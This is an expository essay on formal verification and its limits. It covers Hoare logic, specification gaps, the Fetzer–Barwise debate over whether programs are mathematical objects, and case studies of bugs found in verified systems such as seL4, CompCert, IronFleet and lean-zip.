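# Can software and AI systems be fully reduced to mathematics? What formal specification can and cannot cover

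## What is a formal specification, and what does a proof about a program show?

A formal specification is a statement of what a computer system must do, written in a language with exact mathematical meaning. Formal verification means proving that a system, as described mathematically, meets its specification. Alan Turing sketched the idea in a 1949 talk on checking a long routine, and Robert Floyd turned it into a method for flowcharts in 1967. Tony Hoare's *An Axiomatic Basis for Computer Programming* (1969) adapted the method to programs written as text. *Fifty Years of Hoare's Logic* (Apt and Olderog, 2019) calls his approach the most influential method of verifying programs.

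### From purpose to running process

The term "correct program" can conflate four different things: a purpose, a specification, a program text and a running process. The Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *The Philosophy of Computer Science* gives the example of a phone app whose purpose is to filter out annoying calls from call centres, as customers want. A specification might require the app to keep a list of call-centre numbers, update it every few days, compare each incoming number with the list, and refuse the call if there is a match. A programmer then writes the program text, a string of characters in a language with defined rules. The running process is the series of physical events in one phone when a call comes in.

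Things can go wrong at each step. The phone's memory may fail. The programmer may have compared only the first eight digits. Or the program may do everything in the specification and still let through a call centre that took a new number the day after the last update. Engineers call checking the program against the specification *verification*, and checking the specification against what people need *validation*. A proof can settle verification. For validation, developers use surveys, prototypes and focus groups, because they need to find out what customers want, which they can't prove mathematically. In 1950 Turing drew a related distinction between errors of functioning, where a machine fails to carry out its instructions, and errors of conclusion, where it carries them out but still fails at the task.

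The philosopher Raymond Turner holds that a description becomes a specification when people give it "correctness jurisdiction" over what they are building, so that if a program disagrees with its specification, they change the program. In practice, they sometimes change the specification too, for instance when it misstates what the client wanted. In *Towards a Theory of Bugs*, Stephen Wolfram argues that a program can only have a bug relative to some other statement of what it should do, since it always matches its own behavior.

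### Preconditions, postconditions and a short proof

Proving anything about a program text requires a *semantics*, a set of mathematical rules that define what each text means. An operational semantics consists of rules for evaluating a program down to a final value. A denotational semantics assigns each program a mathematical object, such as a function from inputs to outputs. Hoare instead gave axioms for what holds before and after each kind of instruction. In *Retrospective*, forty years later, Hoare (2009) compared them to Euclid's axioms for measuring land. He had wanted axioms strong enough to help programmers write correct programs, but weak enough to allow very different hardware.

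A *precondition* is what must hold before a program starts, and a *postcondition* is what must hold when it finishes. An earlier edition of the Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy entry specifies the square root y of a number x this way. The precondition is x ≥ 0, and the postcondition is that y·y = x and y ≥ 0. The specification defines the result but not how to find it. An ordinary program can't always meet this specification exactly, because the square root of 2, for example, has infinitely many digits and the program stores only finitely many. A usable version would include a margin of error in the postcondition.

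The *Hoare triple* {P} C {Q} combines a program text C with two assertions, P and Q, which are formulas about the values of variables. It means that if P is true before C starts, and C finishes, then Q is true afterwards.

Hoare's own example divides x by y through repeated subtraction, with all variables ranging over whole numbers from zero up:

`r := x; q := 0; while y ≤ r do (r := r − y; q := 1 + q)`

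The sign := means "store the value on the right under the name on the left". With x = 7 and y = 2, the remainder r takes the values 7, 5, 3, 1 while the quotient q takes the values 0, 1, 2, 3, and the loop stops because 2 ≤ 1 is false. The theorem covers every run, not just this one: whenever the program finishes, x = r + y·q and r < y.

The proof mainly uses two rules. For an assignment v := t, replacing v with t in the condition that must hold afterwards gives the condition that must hold beforehand. For a loop, the rule uses a *loop invariant*, an assertion that each pass through the body preserves whenever the loop condition holds at the start of the pass. If the invariant holds before the loop, it still holds when the loop ends, and the loop condition is then false. The invariant here is x = r + y·q.

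1. Before the loop: working backwards through q := 0 and then r := x turns the invariant into x = x + y·0, which is true of any numbers. So {true} r := x; q := 0 {x = r + y·q}.
2. Inside the loop: working backwards through q := 1 + q and then r := r − y turns the invariant into x = (r − y) + y·(1 + q). If y ≤ r, so that the subtraction makes sense, this multiplies out to x = r + y·q again. One pass therefore preserves the invariant.
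3. After the loop: the invariant still holds and y ≤ r is false, which gives x = r + y·q and r < y.
4. Joining the parts: {true} C {x = r + y·q and r < y}, where C is the whole program. The precondition "true" places no demand on the input.

Steps 1 to 4 are substitution and school algebra. The inventive part was finding the invariant.

If y = 0, the condition 0 ≤ r never fails, and the program keeps subtracting zero forever. The theorem is still true, because a Hoare triple only covers runs that finish. This guarantee is called *partial correctness*, while *total correctness* also requires that the program finish. Hoare was open about this gap, and noted that a program might also fail to finish because it exceeded the machine's storage, its range of numbers or its time limit. He thought it was probably better to prove that the program is correct if it finishes, and have the machine give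 a warning when it had to abandon a run.

To get total correctness for division one can strengthen the precondition to y ≥ 1 and borrow another idea from Turing's 1949 talk, which is to name a quantity that keeps falling and cannot fall forever. The remainder r will do. It drops by at least 1 on each pass and never goes below zero. (No mechanical method can settle termination for every program, a limit that comes up again later, but here the argument takes one line.)

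### A specification that the empty list satisfies

*Djinnlang* (2026) presents a programming language whose compiler uses a large language model, the kind of AI behind chatbots, to write code that meets the programmer's specification. The paper describes sorting a list as the canonical example for any specification language. Suppose a programmer's only postcondition for a sorting program is that the output is in ascending order. A program that ignores its input and always returns the empty list satisfies this, because an empty list has no two elements in the wrong order. A proof that it does would be short and valid.

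The programmer left out the requirement that the output be a rearrangement of the input. *Certification of Bilateral Patience Sort in Theorema and Rocq* (2026) states the corrected specification in the language of Rocq, a program for writing and checking proofs. A function f counts as a sorting algorithm if, for every list l of natural numbers, f(l) is a permutation of l and f(l) is sorted. The proof that a given f qualifies has one part for each condition.

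The repaired specification must also define its terms carefully. For lists without repeated elements, the paper explains "permutation" to mean that whatever occurs in one list also occurs in the other. This is too weak for lists with repeats, because a program that dropped duplicates and turned [2, 2, 1] into [1, 2] would pass. The specification therefore has to count copies. "Ascending" also relies on an assumption about ≤. To show in Djinnlang that sorting has only one possible result, the language model must prove that ≤ is a total order on the elements, which means, among other things, that any two of them are comparable.

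The division theorem has the same kind of gap. A program that ignores its input and sets x to 0, y to 1, r to 0 and q to 0 satisfies the postcondition, x = r + y·q and r < y, without doing any division. To exclude this program, the postcondition must refer to the initial values of x and y. Hoare called his result a necessary but not sufficient condition for the program's correctness.

Such gaps also occur outside textbook examples. In *A benchmark for vericoding*, Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues (2025) assembled 12,504 formal specifications to test how well language models could write programs together with proofs. When they inspected a random sample of the translated specifications by hand, they found a few that allowed trivial solutions. Some had lost content when a language model translated them from one formal language to another, and in others the human author had failed to capture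 the natural-language description. The team also used a second language model to look for the extreme case, a postcondition that is just "true", which every program satisfies. A proof therefore shows only that a program is correct with respect to its specification, and doesn't resolve doubts about the specification itself.

### Ways of checking

Testing means running the program on chosen inputs and comparing the results with the specification. As Edsger Dijkstra remarked in 1970, it can reveal a fault but can never show that none is left. For example, Wolfram looked for Turing machines (very simple abstract computers that read and write symbols on a tape) with three states and two symbols that add 1 to a number. One machine gives the right answer for every input from 0 to 14, but for 15 it gives 20. *Model checking* represents the program as a set of states with transitions between them,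 and an algorithm searches these for a violation of the stated property. A completed search that finds no violation covers every run of that mathematical description, but people usually have to go back to testing to check whether the description fits the actual program.

*Type checking* takes less work but establishes only that each operation receives the right kind of data, so that a program never tries to multiply a number by a name. The empty-list program would pass, since it does return a list. In *interactive proof*, a person builds the argument step by step in a proof assistant such as Rocq or Lean, and the theorem can cover infinitely many inputs. A language model can now do some of this too. Wolfram had one construct a proof that a certain two-state Turing machine adds 1 to every number, and a proof assistant validated the steps. A *proof checker* then confirms that each step of the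 finished proof follows from the rules, regardless of how the proof was found. Because the checker can be a fairly small program, it is easier to verify than the large tools that search for proofs. It does not check whether the theorem was worth proving, and users still have to check what they submit. Bursuc and colleagues screened the AI-written answers for known shortcuts, including Lean's keyword *sorry*, which stands in for a missing proof.

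### Programs that nobody wrote to a specification

A neural network is a function that uses arithmetic to turn input numbers into output numbers. One of its units, with two inputs a and b, might compute max(0, 0.8·a − 0.5·b + 0.1). It multiplies each input by a fixed *weight*, adds the results and a constant, and replaces a negative total with zero. For a = 1 and b = 1, this gives 0.4. A network feeds the outputs of many such units into further layers of units, and the largest networks have many billions of weights. An image classifier of this kind turns pixel values into a score for each label. A language model turns text, encoded as numbers, into a probability for each possible next word or piece of a word.

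Developers choose the layout of the units and a *loss*, a number that measures how far the outputs fall short on a collection of examples. They don't choose the individual weights, which a training algorithm adjusts in many small steps to reduce the loss. The loss is mathematically exact, but it measures performance on examples, whereas a postcondition constrains the output for every permitted input. The developers of a network that tells cats from dogs have labelled photographs rather than an invariant like the one Hoare's loop preserves. The trained network, with its final weights, is an *AI model*; an *AI system* is that model together with its tools, permissions, users and surroundings.

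A Hoare triple can describe a trained network, with C as the network's arithmetic, P restricting the inputs and Q restricting the outputs. But it is hard to find a formula Q that means "the label is *cat* if and only if the picture shows a cat".

### Three questions in one

Whether software and AI can be fully reduced to mathematics is three questions, and a system can do well on one and badly on another. The first is whether the system is a mathematical object. The division program is one if "program" means the text with its semantics. The phone or laptop that runs it is physical, and people have disputed since the 1970s how much a proof about the text can establish about the machine.

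People can state the properties they want from sorting, though doing so took more than one attempt. To do the same for the call filter, somebody would first have to define "annoying".

Even when a rule and a property are both stated exactly, there may be no obvious way to check that the property always holds. Wolfram describes a cellular automaton, a row of cells that change colour by a fixed rule, which appears to double the length of any block of coloured cells it starts from. He ran it on blocks of up to 100,000 cells without a failure, but saw no obvious way to be sure that the next one would not fail.

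## Is a program a mathematical object?

Hoare thought so. His 1969 paper opens with the claim that programming is an exact science because people can in principle deduce from a program's text all its properties and all the consequences of running it "in any given environment". Twenty years later, computer scientists were quarrelling over that sentence, and two of the main participants, the philosopher James Fetzer and the logician Jon Barwise, had quoted it without the four words about the environment. Barwise had copied it from an article by Fetzer into *Mathematical Proofs of Computer System Correctness* (1989). When the mathematician Richard Dudley complained, Barwise admitted the mistake and passed on Fetzer's explanation that the ellipsis in earlier versions of his own article had somehow disappeared.

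The missing words make Hoare's claim more modest, but Barwise thought it was still ambiguous. "Environment" can mean the physical surroundings in which a computer runs a program, or an abstract object in computer scientists' mathematical description. Barwise said people can prove a program correct only if the word has its abstract meaning, and how useful the proof is depends on how well the description fits the machine.

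Hoare's paper suggests that he saw the difference, because it leaves the electronics outside the proof. He wrote that once people have established the correctness of the program, its compiler (which translates the program into machine instructions) and the hardware, they can predict the results with a confidence "limited only by the reliability of the electronics".

### Programs as mathematical expressions

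Hoare put the view more strongly in the magazine *Byte* in 1986. He wrote that computers are mathematical machines and that "computer programs are mathematical expressions", that a programming language is a mathematical theory, and that programming is a mathematical activity. Fetzer quoted from this passage too, and Dudley pointed out in his letter to Barwise that Hoare had followed it with a "However" in capitals. Hoare called his statements philosophical and moral principles and admitted that "all the actual evidence is against them". He said that computers, programs, programming languages and even programmers were not as he had described them. Dudley took him to be recommending how programmers should work in future.

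Edsger Dijkstra made fewer concessions. In a 1988 essay on teaching computer science, he described a program as an abstract symbol manipulator, which people can make concrete by supplying a computer. On this view, the machine exists to execute the program. He wanted first-year students to learn in a programming language that no computer on campus could run, so they would not be tempted to test their programs.

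Hoare's list does have an exact reading. A *state* is an assignment of values to all of a program's variables. The meaning of a program text is then a set of pairs, each containing a state in which a run can start and the state in which that run ends. For the division program of the previous section, one pair starts with x = 7 and y = 2 and ends with q = 3 and r = 1. No pair starts with y = 0, because those runs never end.

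Each construction in the language is an operation on such sets. Writing one instruction after another joins their pairs wherever the end state of the first is the start state of the second. An "if" keeps only the pairs whose first state satisfies the condition. The Hoare triple {P} C {Q} means that in every pair in the set C whose first state satisfies P, the second state satisfies Q. None of these definitions refers to a machine, and a mathematician could have studied them before anyone had built a computer.

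### Proofs that nobody reads

In *Social Processes and Proofs of Theorems and Programs*, De Millo, Lipton and Perlis (1979) attacked program verification but agreed that a program is a formal object. They thought the verifiers were mistaken about mathematics.

They argued that a written proof does not by itself make mathematicians believe a theorem. In 1879 Alfred Kempe published a proof that four colours are enough to colour any map, and it stood for eleven years before Percy Heawood found a fatal flaw. More recently, an American and a Japanese team had announced contradictory results about the same topological object and exchanged proofs, but neither could find the other's error. A third group then obtained a proof that supported the Americans. Mathematicians come to trust a theorem by explaining it to colleagues, refereeing it, putting it in their own words, generalising it and using it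 in other proofs.

Nobody would do this for a program verification, because the proofs are long, shallow and dull. De Millo, Lipton and Perlis printed a condition that had to be proved to verify a program for the fast Fourier transform, a standard calculation in signal processing, and it is a dense mass of symbols. They also pointed out that real specifications are messy; the French national railway's payroll, for example, needed more than 3,000 pay rates, including one for uphill and one for downhill. Programs also change all the time, and a verification of one version may not carry over to another that differs by a single line. They concluded that verification was "bound to fail". In an earlier conference paper with the same title, they had been more hopeful, and saw every reason to believe that social mechanisms could make verification more like ordinary mathematics.

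The natural reply is to have a machine check the proofs. De Millo and colleagues had already considered this, imagining a programmer who feeds 300 lines into an automatic verifier and gets back a 20,000-line proof with the message "VERIFIED". They wrote that believing the message would be blind faith, and that a verifier would never return it for a real program anyway.

That prediction was wrong. Paulson (2025), in *The philosophical problem of induction, and the problem of Fetzer*, describes seL4, the core of an operating system, as fully verified in all its functions. The charge of blind faith is also weaker now. Many people inspect the same small proof checker and use it for many different proofs, so the social process can apply to the checker and the statement of the theorem without anyone reading the 20,000 lines.

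Two of their objections hold no matter who reads the proof. People's requirements start out informal and the program is formal, so getting from one to the other requires an informal step. And a specification is a useful check on a program only if people arrived at the two independently. But in practice, when a program fails, programmers change either the program or the specification with the other in view. Lipton (2022), in *Discussion About Proving Again*, still defends a narrower form of the argument, that the correctness of real systems is very complex and full of separate cases, and that mathematical proof is not suited to such huge statements.

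### Fetzer's argument

Fetzer shared the pessimism of De Millo and colleagues but thought that their reasons were wrong. They had taken the proof sketches in mathematics journals for real proofs, he said. His own objection was about what kind of thing a program is. Fetzer (1988), in *Program Verification: The Very Idea*, argued that a completely reliable general method of guaranteeing what programs do is "not even a theoretical possibility". Reconstructed in steps, the argument is:

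1. The purpose of program verification is to guarantee what a program will do when a machine runs it.
2. Deductive proof gives conclusive knowledge only of abstract things.
3. An algorithm, the step-by-step method behind a program, is an abstract logical structure, so people can prove conclusively that it has some property.
4. A program that a machine can run is a cause inside a physical system.
5. People know how physical systems behave only through experience, and such knowledge is always uncertain.
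6. Therefore no proof can guarantee what a program will do.

Fetzer called conclusive proof about abstract things "absolute" verification. For machines he allowed only "relative" verification, which is never conclusive.

William Rapaport's *Can Programs Be Verified?* lists fourteen letters about Fetzer's article in *Communications of the ACM*, the magazine that had published it. One of them, *Editorial Process Verification* (Ardis, Basili, Gerhart and colleagues, 1989), called the article "ill-informed, irresponsible, and dangerous". It rejected the first premise as a straw man, since Fetzer had cited nobody who promised an absolute guarantee about execution on hardware. Fetzer replied that the idea, if not the phrase, was in the work of Hoare and Dijkstra.

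There is evidence on both sides. *Mathematical checking of programs (quoting Tony Hoare)*, a forum post by henry (1986), quotes Hoare calling proof "technically, a completely reliable method" of ensuring that programs are correct, though a "but" follows in the same sentence. Hoare's 1969 remark about the reliability of the electronics supports the other side. The premise fits some of Hoare's and Dijkstra's more sweeping statements better than it fits what most people in the field were trying to do.

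Ardis and colleagues also objected that researchers had already applied formal methods to compilers, operating systems and hardware. Fetzer correctly answered that these are physical things too, so his argument applies equally to them. A proof about a circuit covers only a description of it, and the manufactured chip may differ from that description.

The fourth premise is weaker, because "program" can mean two things. Barwise distinguished a program as a *type*, an abstract object, from its *instances*, the physical copies. Only an instance can cause anything, and a proof is about the type. Holes in a paper tape or charges in a memory cell represent a program much as ink on paper represents the formula f(x) = x², and the ink doesn't make the formula physical. Fetzer put the boundary between the abstract and the physical at the step from algorithms to programs, but it seems to belong between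 program texts and running processes, because a text with a semantics is as abstract as any algorithm.

The comparison with ink is limited because charges in a memory cell can open a valve without anyone reading them, while ink on a page does nothing until someone reads it. This is presumably why people so easily slip from claims about the text to claims about the valve. E. G. Daylight, who defends Fetzer, complains that verification researchers often say "computer program" when they mean another representation of the program.

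### Barwise's reply: applied mathematics

Several of Fetzer's critics accepted that verification is about physical computers and gave up the claim to mathematical certainty. Barwise reports that William Bevier, Michael Smith and William Young treated verification as a physical science that aims at highly accurate predictions. They argued that describing hardware and software in enough detail, down to the logic gates, makes the gap between mathematics and machine too small to matter. A physical AND gate does not always behave like the Boolean function AND, but denying any relation between the two would mean denying that mathematics can describe anything real, which would also make physics impossible.

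John Dobson and Brian Randell, writing in the same magazine, argued that verifiers had oversold their work and that Fetzer had confused the reason something is so with a reason for believing it. A proof about a sorting program is evidence that the machine will sort, because it rules out certain kinds of error, but it does not make the machine sort. In their view, people can falsify the hypothesis that a program will execute correctly but can never prove it.

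Barwise thought that Bevier and his colleagues had conceded too much, since verification could be a science and still be mathematics. It is applied mathematics, with the same limits as any other branch. An astronomer who predicts an orbit proves theorems about equations. The theorems are informative about the planet if the equations fit it, but this usually can't be proved. People judge the fit from experience, or sometimes from knowing how the system being modeled works.

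Barwise called forgetting this step the *Fallacy of Identification*, the failure to distinguish a mathematical description from the thing it describes. Mathematicians routinely treat the two as the same while they work, and Barwise wrote that this does no harm as long as they remember the difference once the proof is finished. He found that writers on verification often left it unclear whether their theorems were about a description of a computer or a real computer.

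Barwise also charged Fetzer with the same fallacy. Fetzer had defined a proof as a sequence of formulas in which each is either given or follows from earlier ones by a rule. Barwise objected that this is a logician's mathematical description of proofs, and that people had been proving theorems for thousands of years before logicians invented it. He gave the example of a mathematician who proves one case and says that the others follow by symmetry, a step for which he knew of no general formal rule. The example is weaker now that proof assistants have commands that expand such a step into ordinary formal ones, but the distinction between proofs and the logician's description of them still holds.

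The two sides were closer than their tone suggested. Fetzer later insisted in an online discussion that he had always accepted verification as a branch of applied mathematics. In *Some Issues Lying Beneath a Recent Exchange of Views*, Fetzer (1990) denied that formal proofs can guarantee a program's performance, but affirmed that they give inconclusive evidence of it and should be one method among several. Charlie Martin, who had been trading abuse with him in the same forum, replied that he could disagree with effectively none of it. Another participant, Ralph Johnson, pointed out that nothing else, including testing, gives an absolute guarantee either. That seems to me the right verdict, because Fetzer's conclusion is true but proofs can't guarantee how a bridge will perform either.

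Lawrence Paulson, who co-signed one of the letters against Fetzer in 1989, still holds that Fetzer's argument works only against someone who thinks verification makes testing unnecessary. He prefers a paper that his colleague Avra Cohn published the same year. Cohn had worked on proofs about Viper, a British microprocessor, and she criticised exaggerated claims about how much had been verified. Fetzer welcomed her paper too, although she had co-signed the same letter as Paulson.

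Paulson reports that the developers of seL4 still test the parts that the proof takes as assumptions, the speed of the code, and whether the verified functions do what people intended. But tests of software are a poor guide to untested cases. After a short drive, someone can guess how an ordinary car will handle a hill, but Paulson compares a program to a car that drives beautifully and yet might explode if exactly 26 leaves blew underneath it.

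### One addition, five kinds of arithmetic

A claim that is true in ordinary arithmetic can be false on a computer, even for a single addition. One such claim is that if x ≥ 0, then x + 1 > 0, which can be written as the Hoare triple {x ≥ 0} y := x + 1 {y > 0}. It is true for the whole numbers of school arithmetic. But a computer that stores each integer in 32 binary digits can represent only 2³² values, commonly those from −2,147,483,648 to 2,147,483,647. On many machines, adding 1 to the largest value *wraps around* to the smallest. For x = 2,147,483,647 the result is then −2,147,483,648, so the claim is false.

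Hoare dealt with this problem in 1969. He listed nine axioms for non-negative integers, such as x + y = y + x, and then three ways a machine might handle a result too large for it, each with its own axiom. In the table, "max" stands for the largest integer the machine can represent.

| Arithmetic | Value of max + 1 | Is the triple true? |
|---|---|---|
| Unlimited whole numbers | there is no max | yes |
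| Strict: an oversized result does not exist, and the program never completes | none | yes, because the triple covers only runs that finish |
| Firm boundary | max | yes |
| Modulo, with non-negative integers only | 0 | no |
| Wrapping, with negative integers | the smallest integer | no |

Hoare's nine axioms are true in the first four rows. The division proof in the previous section uses only these axioms and the usual facts about order, so it holds however the machine treats overflow. The claim about x + 1 cannot be derived from the nine axioms alone, because it is false in modulo arithmetic, where all nine are true. To prove it, a programmer has to add an axiom about overflow, and Hoare warned that properties deduced from that axiom may not hold on an implementation that does not satisfy it.

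A semantics with machine integers therefore exposes the error. A proof of the triple for wrapping 32-bit integers fails at x = 2,147,483,647, and strengthening the precondition to 0 ≤ x < 2,147,483,647 makes the triple provable. The same characters can also mean different things in different languages. In Python, the integer result of x + 1 has no upper limit, while in Java it wraps if x is a 32-bit int. So a string of characters has no mathematical properties of this kind until someone fixes a semantics for it.

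Now suppose a manufacturing fault leaves the wire for the last binary digit of every sum stuck at 0. For x = 0, the machine computes 0 + 1 and stores 0 instead of 1. The repaired triple is still a theorem, but the machine violates it. Engineers could write a more detailed semantics that includes stuck wires, or design a circuit and prove that it gives the right answer as long as at most one wire is stuck. But "at most one wire is stuck" is a claim about the physical chip, and somebody has to find out whether it is true.

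### Which function does the machine compute?

Calling the chip faulty assumes that its job is to add. In *Wittgenstein on Rules and Private Language* (1982), the philosopher Saul Kripke argued that the physical facts about a machine do not determine what its job is. A machine that gives −2,147,483,648 for 2,147,483,647 + 1 could be a defective adder of whole numbers or a working adder of wrapping integers.

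Kripke concluded that a machine malfunctions only relative to a program that its designer has stipulated. If the machine computes whatever function its actual answers form, it can never malfunction. Saying that it computes the function it would compute if no wire melted and no gear slipped assumes we already know which physical changes count as breakdowns, which is what we were trying to establish. Kripke's conclusion fits Turner's view of specifications, since examining an artefact alone would not reveal which description people had given authority over it.

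The mathematical function that a logic gate computes depends on which voltage stands for 1 and which for 0. Suppose a gate's output voltage is high when both input voltages are high and low otherwise. If high stands for 1 and low for 0, the gate computes AND. If the assignment is reversed, it computes OR, because its output is 0 only when both inputs are 0.

A machine cannot be interpreted as computing just any function. No relabelling of the two voltages turns this gate into exclusive-or, which is 1 when exactly one input is 1. Exclusive-or gives each of its two answers for two of the four input pairs, while the gate gives one voltage for three pairs and the other for one, however the voltages are labelled. Physics rules out most functions, and people choose among the rest. For a commercial chip, these choices are usually public, because the manufacturer states in the manual which voltages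 stand for 1 and what happens on overflow. Kripke's argument therefore gives engineers no reason to distrust their chips, though it does mean that "this machine computes addition" is partly a statement about what people have decided.

### What "reducible to mathematics" can mean

In one sense, then, software can be reduced to mathematics. A program text with a fixed semantics is a mathematical object, and its properties follow from the definitions, whether or not anyone can find the deduction. The same is true of a trained neural network, if "network" means its weights and the precise arithmetic that combines them, including rounding. Dudley's letter mentions that when computers keep a fixed number of digits, the order of additions can change the result. With three significant digits, (1000 + 4) + 4 gives 1000, because each 4 is lost to rounding, but 1000 + (4 + 4) gives 1010. A description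 of a network must therefore fix the order of its additions to specify which function the network computes.

Fetzer was right that a program's text does not determine what will happen in the machine, and Hoare had already made an exception for the electronics.

In a trivial sense, some mathematical description also fits every machine, since a table of inputs and outputs can describe any finite record of what a machine did. A specification can be just as empty. Suppose the only requirement on the call filter of the previous section is that it either refuses each call or does not. Then logic alone proves that every phone meets the specification, even one with a flat battery. Peter Ladkin, in *Fetzer* (2019), says that Fetzer's argument fails because he left specifications out of it. Strictly speaking, the example supports Ladkin, since it is a conclusive proof about physical objects, but the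 phone's owner learns nothing from it. If a specification excludes anything a phone could conceivably do, knowing that the phone meets it requires evidence about the phone.

For computers, that evidence is often good. Barwise thought the mathematical descriptions behind correctness proofs were "in above average shape" by the standards of applied mathematics, because people build computers and know quite well how programs act on them. He was much less confident about descriptions of the users and surroundings.

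## What has gone wrong in software that was proved correct?

If Fetzer was right that no proof can guarantee what a machine will do, verified software should sometimes fail, but we can't work out from his argument how often or why. Researchers have since tested a few verified systems hard enough to find faults, and they could usually tell which layer caused them.

### What the seL4 proofs assume

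seL4 is an operating system kernel, the program that controls every other program's access to memory and devices. Its developers have proved that the kernel's C code does what a formal specification requires. This rules out whole classes of common mistakes, such as buffer overflows, in which a program writes past the end of a block of memory. On some processors a further proof links the C code to the binary code that the machine executes, so nobody has to trust the compiler. There are also proofs of integrity and confidentiality, though seL4's developers note that not every platform has every proof.

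The project publishes its assumptions in seL4's *What the Proofs Assume*. The main ones are:

- About 340 lines of assembly code (in the ARM version) are correct. They mostly handle entry to and exit from the kernel.
- About 1,200 lines of boot code leave the kernel in a consistent initial state.
- The hardware works as specified, nobody has tampered with it, and the kernel manages its caches correctly.
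- Devices that can write directly to memory are absent or behave themselves, since one of them could overwrite the kernel.
- For confidentiality only, the mathematical description of the hardware includes every channel through which information can leak.

The developers write of the last assumption, "We know this not to be the case." Their proof covers information stored inside the kernel but not timing, so one program might still learn about another by measuring how long operations take. They also assume that their logic is consistent and that the proof assistant Isabelle checked the proof correctly, but they think the assumptions about code and hardware are much more likely to cause problems.

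The developers review the unproved low-level code by hand. Paulson reported that they also still test the proof's assumptions. They think verification could in theory cover the rest of the software, but some assumptions about the physical world would always remain.

### Random tests for C compilers

Yang, Chen and colleagues spent three years looking for bugs in compilers for the programming language C (*Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers*, 2011). Their tool, Csmith, generates random C programs, each of which prints a number computed from the final values of its variables. The team compiled each program with several compilers, ran the compiled versions and compared the numbers. If one version printed a different number from the majority, the compiler that produced it was probably wrong.

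This method works without knowing the right answer in advance, but each test program must have only one right answer. The C standard has 191 kinds of undefined behaviour, such as overflowing a signed integer, after which a program no longer has any meaning. In 52 other situations, a compiler may choose among several options. Csmith therefore had to generate programs that avoided undefined behaviour and whose output did not depend on the compiler's choices.

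The team reported more than 325 previously unknown bugs to 11 compiler teams, including 79 in GCC and 202 in LLVM, two widely used open-source compilers. Every compiler they tested crashed on some valid programs and silently mistranslated others.

One of the eleven was CompCert, a compiler with machine-checked proofs that its optimisations preserve a program's meaning. Csmith exposed six bugs that produced wrong code in CompCert's front end, the unverified part that first processes the C text. One involved the expression `-1 <= (1 && x)`. The part in brackets is always 0 or 1, so the comparison is true and should give 1. CompCert's code gave 0, as it would if the compiler had treated −1 as the unsigned 32-bit number 4,294,967,295.

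Two more bugs came from CompCert's formal description of the PowerPC processor. One instruction has a 16-bit field for a distance in memory, and the field can only hold values from −32,768 to 32,767. The description left out this limit, and CompCert put −44,432 in the field. The developers had relied on the assembler, the next tool in the chain, to reject such values, and it did. CompCert also crashed on a handful of programs.

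CompCert's main developer then extended the proof to more of the front end. By early 2011, the version under development was the only compiler in which Csmith could find no wrong-code bugs, after about six CPU-years of testing. CompCert was also the only one without bugs in the middle stages, where optimisation happens.

### Three distributed systems

A distributed system is a group of computers that cooperate over a network, for instance by keeping copies of the same data so that no data is lost if one computer crashes. The rules that keep the copies consistent, called a protocol, are notoriously hard to program. Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues (2017), in *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems*, examined three research prototypes with verified protocols. IronFleet uses Dafny, a programming language with its own verifier, while Verdi and Chapar use Rocq,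 then called Coq. The team read the code, tested the systems with duplicated packets, interrupted disk writes and spurious errors, and found 16 bugs.

Eleven of the bugs were in the *shim layer*, the mostly unverified code that connects the verified part to the network and the disk. Verdi's developers had assumed that one call to the operating system would deliver a client's whole request, and the server crashed when only part of it had arrived. The server also replaced its snapshot of the data every 1,000 events, but it deleted the old snapshot before it had safely written the new one, so a crash between the two steps would lose data. Chapar's proof assumed a reliable network, but its servers exchanged updates over UDP, which can lose or duplicate packets.

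One of the eleven involved a function that Coq had generated from verified code. The function crashed the server when another server had fallen more than 500,000 requests behind, because it calls itself for each missing entry and each call uses some memory until none is left. The proof did not cover memory use, a gap that Hoare had pointed out in 1969.

Two bugs were in specifications. A client that gets no answer usually repeats its request, and the server should then carry it out only once. IronFleet's server did this, but its specification did not require it. Fonseca and colleagues disabled this safeguard by changing seven lines, and the server still passed verification. They also proved that the specification allowed a counter to reach any value after a single operation. IronFleet's developers replied that they had known about the omission and did not consider it a bug, because they did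 not take the guarantee to include this requirement. In Chapar, an assertion in an example program repeated a condition that the program had just tested, so it could never fail.

The other three bugs were in IronFleet's verification tools. The distribution combined a 64-bit prover with 32-bit libraries, which made the prover crash. The build tool read only the verifier's first message, which listed no errors, and missed the second, which reported the crash. It therefore passed any program, including one that asserted something false. Dafny also reported files as verified if a user interrupted verification.

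The team spent more than eight months on the search and found no mistakes in the protocols. They also looked at a year of bug reports for four unverified systems with similar protocols. Of the 555 bugs in that sample, 12 were protocol bugs, and each system had at least one.

### When the hardware departs from its description

The timing channels that seL4's proof leaves out became notorious in 2018, when researchers disclosed the Spectre attacks. Many processors save time by guessing which instructions will come next and running them early. If the guess is wrong, the processor discards the results, so the program's output still matches the behavior described in the manual. But the discarded instructions leave traces in the cache, a small, fast memory, and an attacker can recover secrets by timing memory accesses. A mathematical description that contains only registers and main memory cannot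 represent these traces, so a confidentiality proof based on it would remain valid even if the machine leaked secrets this way.

Hardware can also malfunction. OpenAI investigated crashes in its data infrastructure in which a C++ function finished and then returned to a bogus address. In some of them the stack pointer, the processor register that marks the current position in working memory, was off by 8 bytes. Performance Golf's *Engineers Identify Hardware Fault and Software Bug Through Core Dump Analysis* (2026), a short AI-written summary, attributes the crashes to a hardware fault and an 18-year-old software bug. This is thin evidence, and nobody had claimed to have verified the C++ code, but a proof about that code would not have prevented a hardware fault.

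### Faults in verified software in 2026

By 2026, AI agents were writing verified programs and other AI agents were attacking them. Ten agents built lean-zip, a compression program in Lean. One of its main theorems states that, for any input under a gigabyte, decompressing the compressed data gives back the original. A compressor and decompressor that both left the data unchanged would also satisfy this theorem. *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes an experiment in which the AI model Claude spent a night *fuzzing* lean-zip, which means running it on many automatically altered inputs. In more than 105 million runs, Claude found no memory faults in the verified code.

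It did find two bugs elsewhere. The first was in Lean's runtime, the C++ code beneath every Lean program, which calculated how much memory to reserve by adding 24 to the requested size. For a request of 2⁶⁴ − 1 bytes, the sum wrapped around and the runtime reserved 23 bytes. The second was in the code that reads the headers of ZIP archives. There were no theorems about this code, and it used the size given in the header without comparing it with the actual file, so a 156-byte file could make the program run out of memory and crash.

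*Zero-Trust Formal Methods* (2026) describes a project in which agents wrote verified programs to check the answers of automatic solvers. Reviewers found defects in the specifications and in the code that the proofs assumed was correct. One defect, at a point where two unverified components read the same text, allowed a spurious proof. The project also had to assume that the front end of Verus, a verifier for Rust, was correct, although such front ends have bugs.

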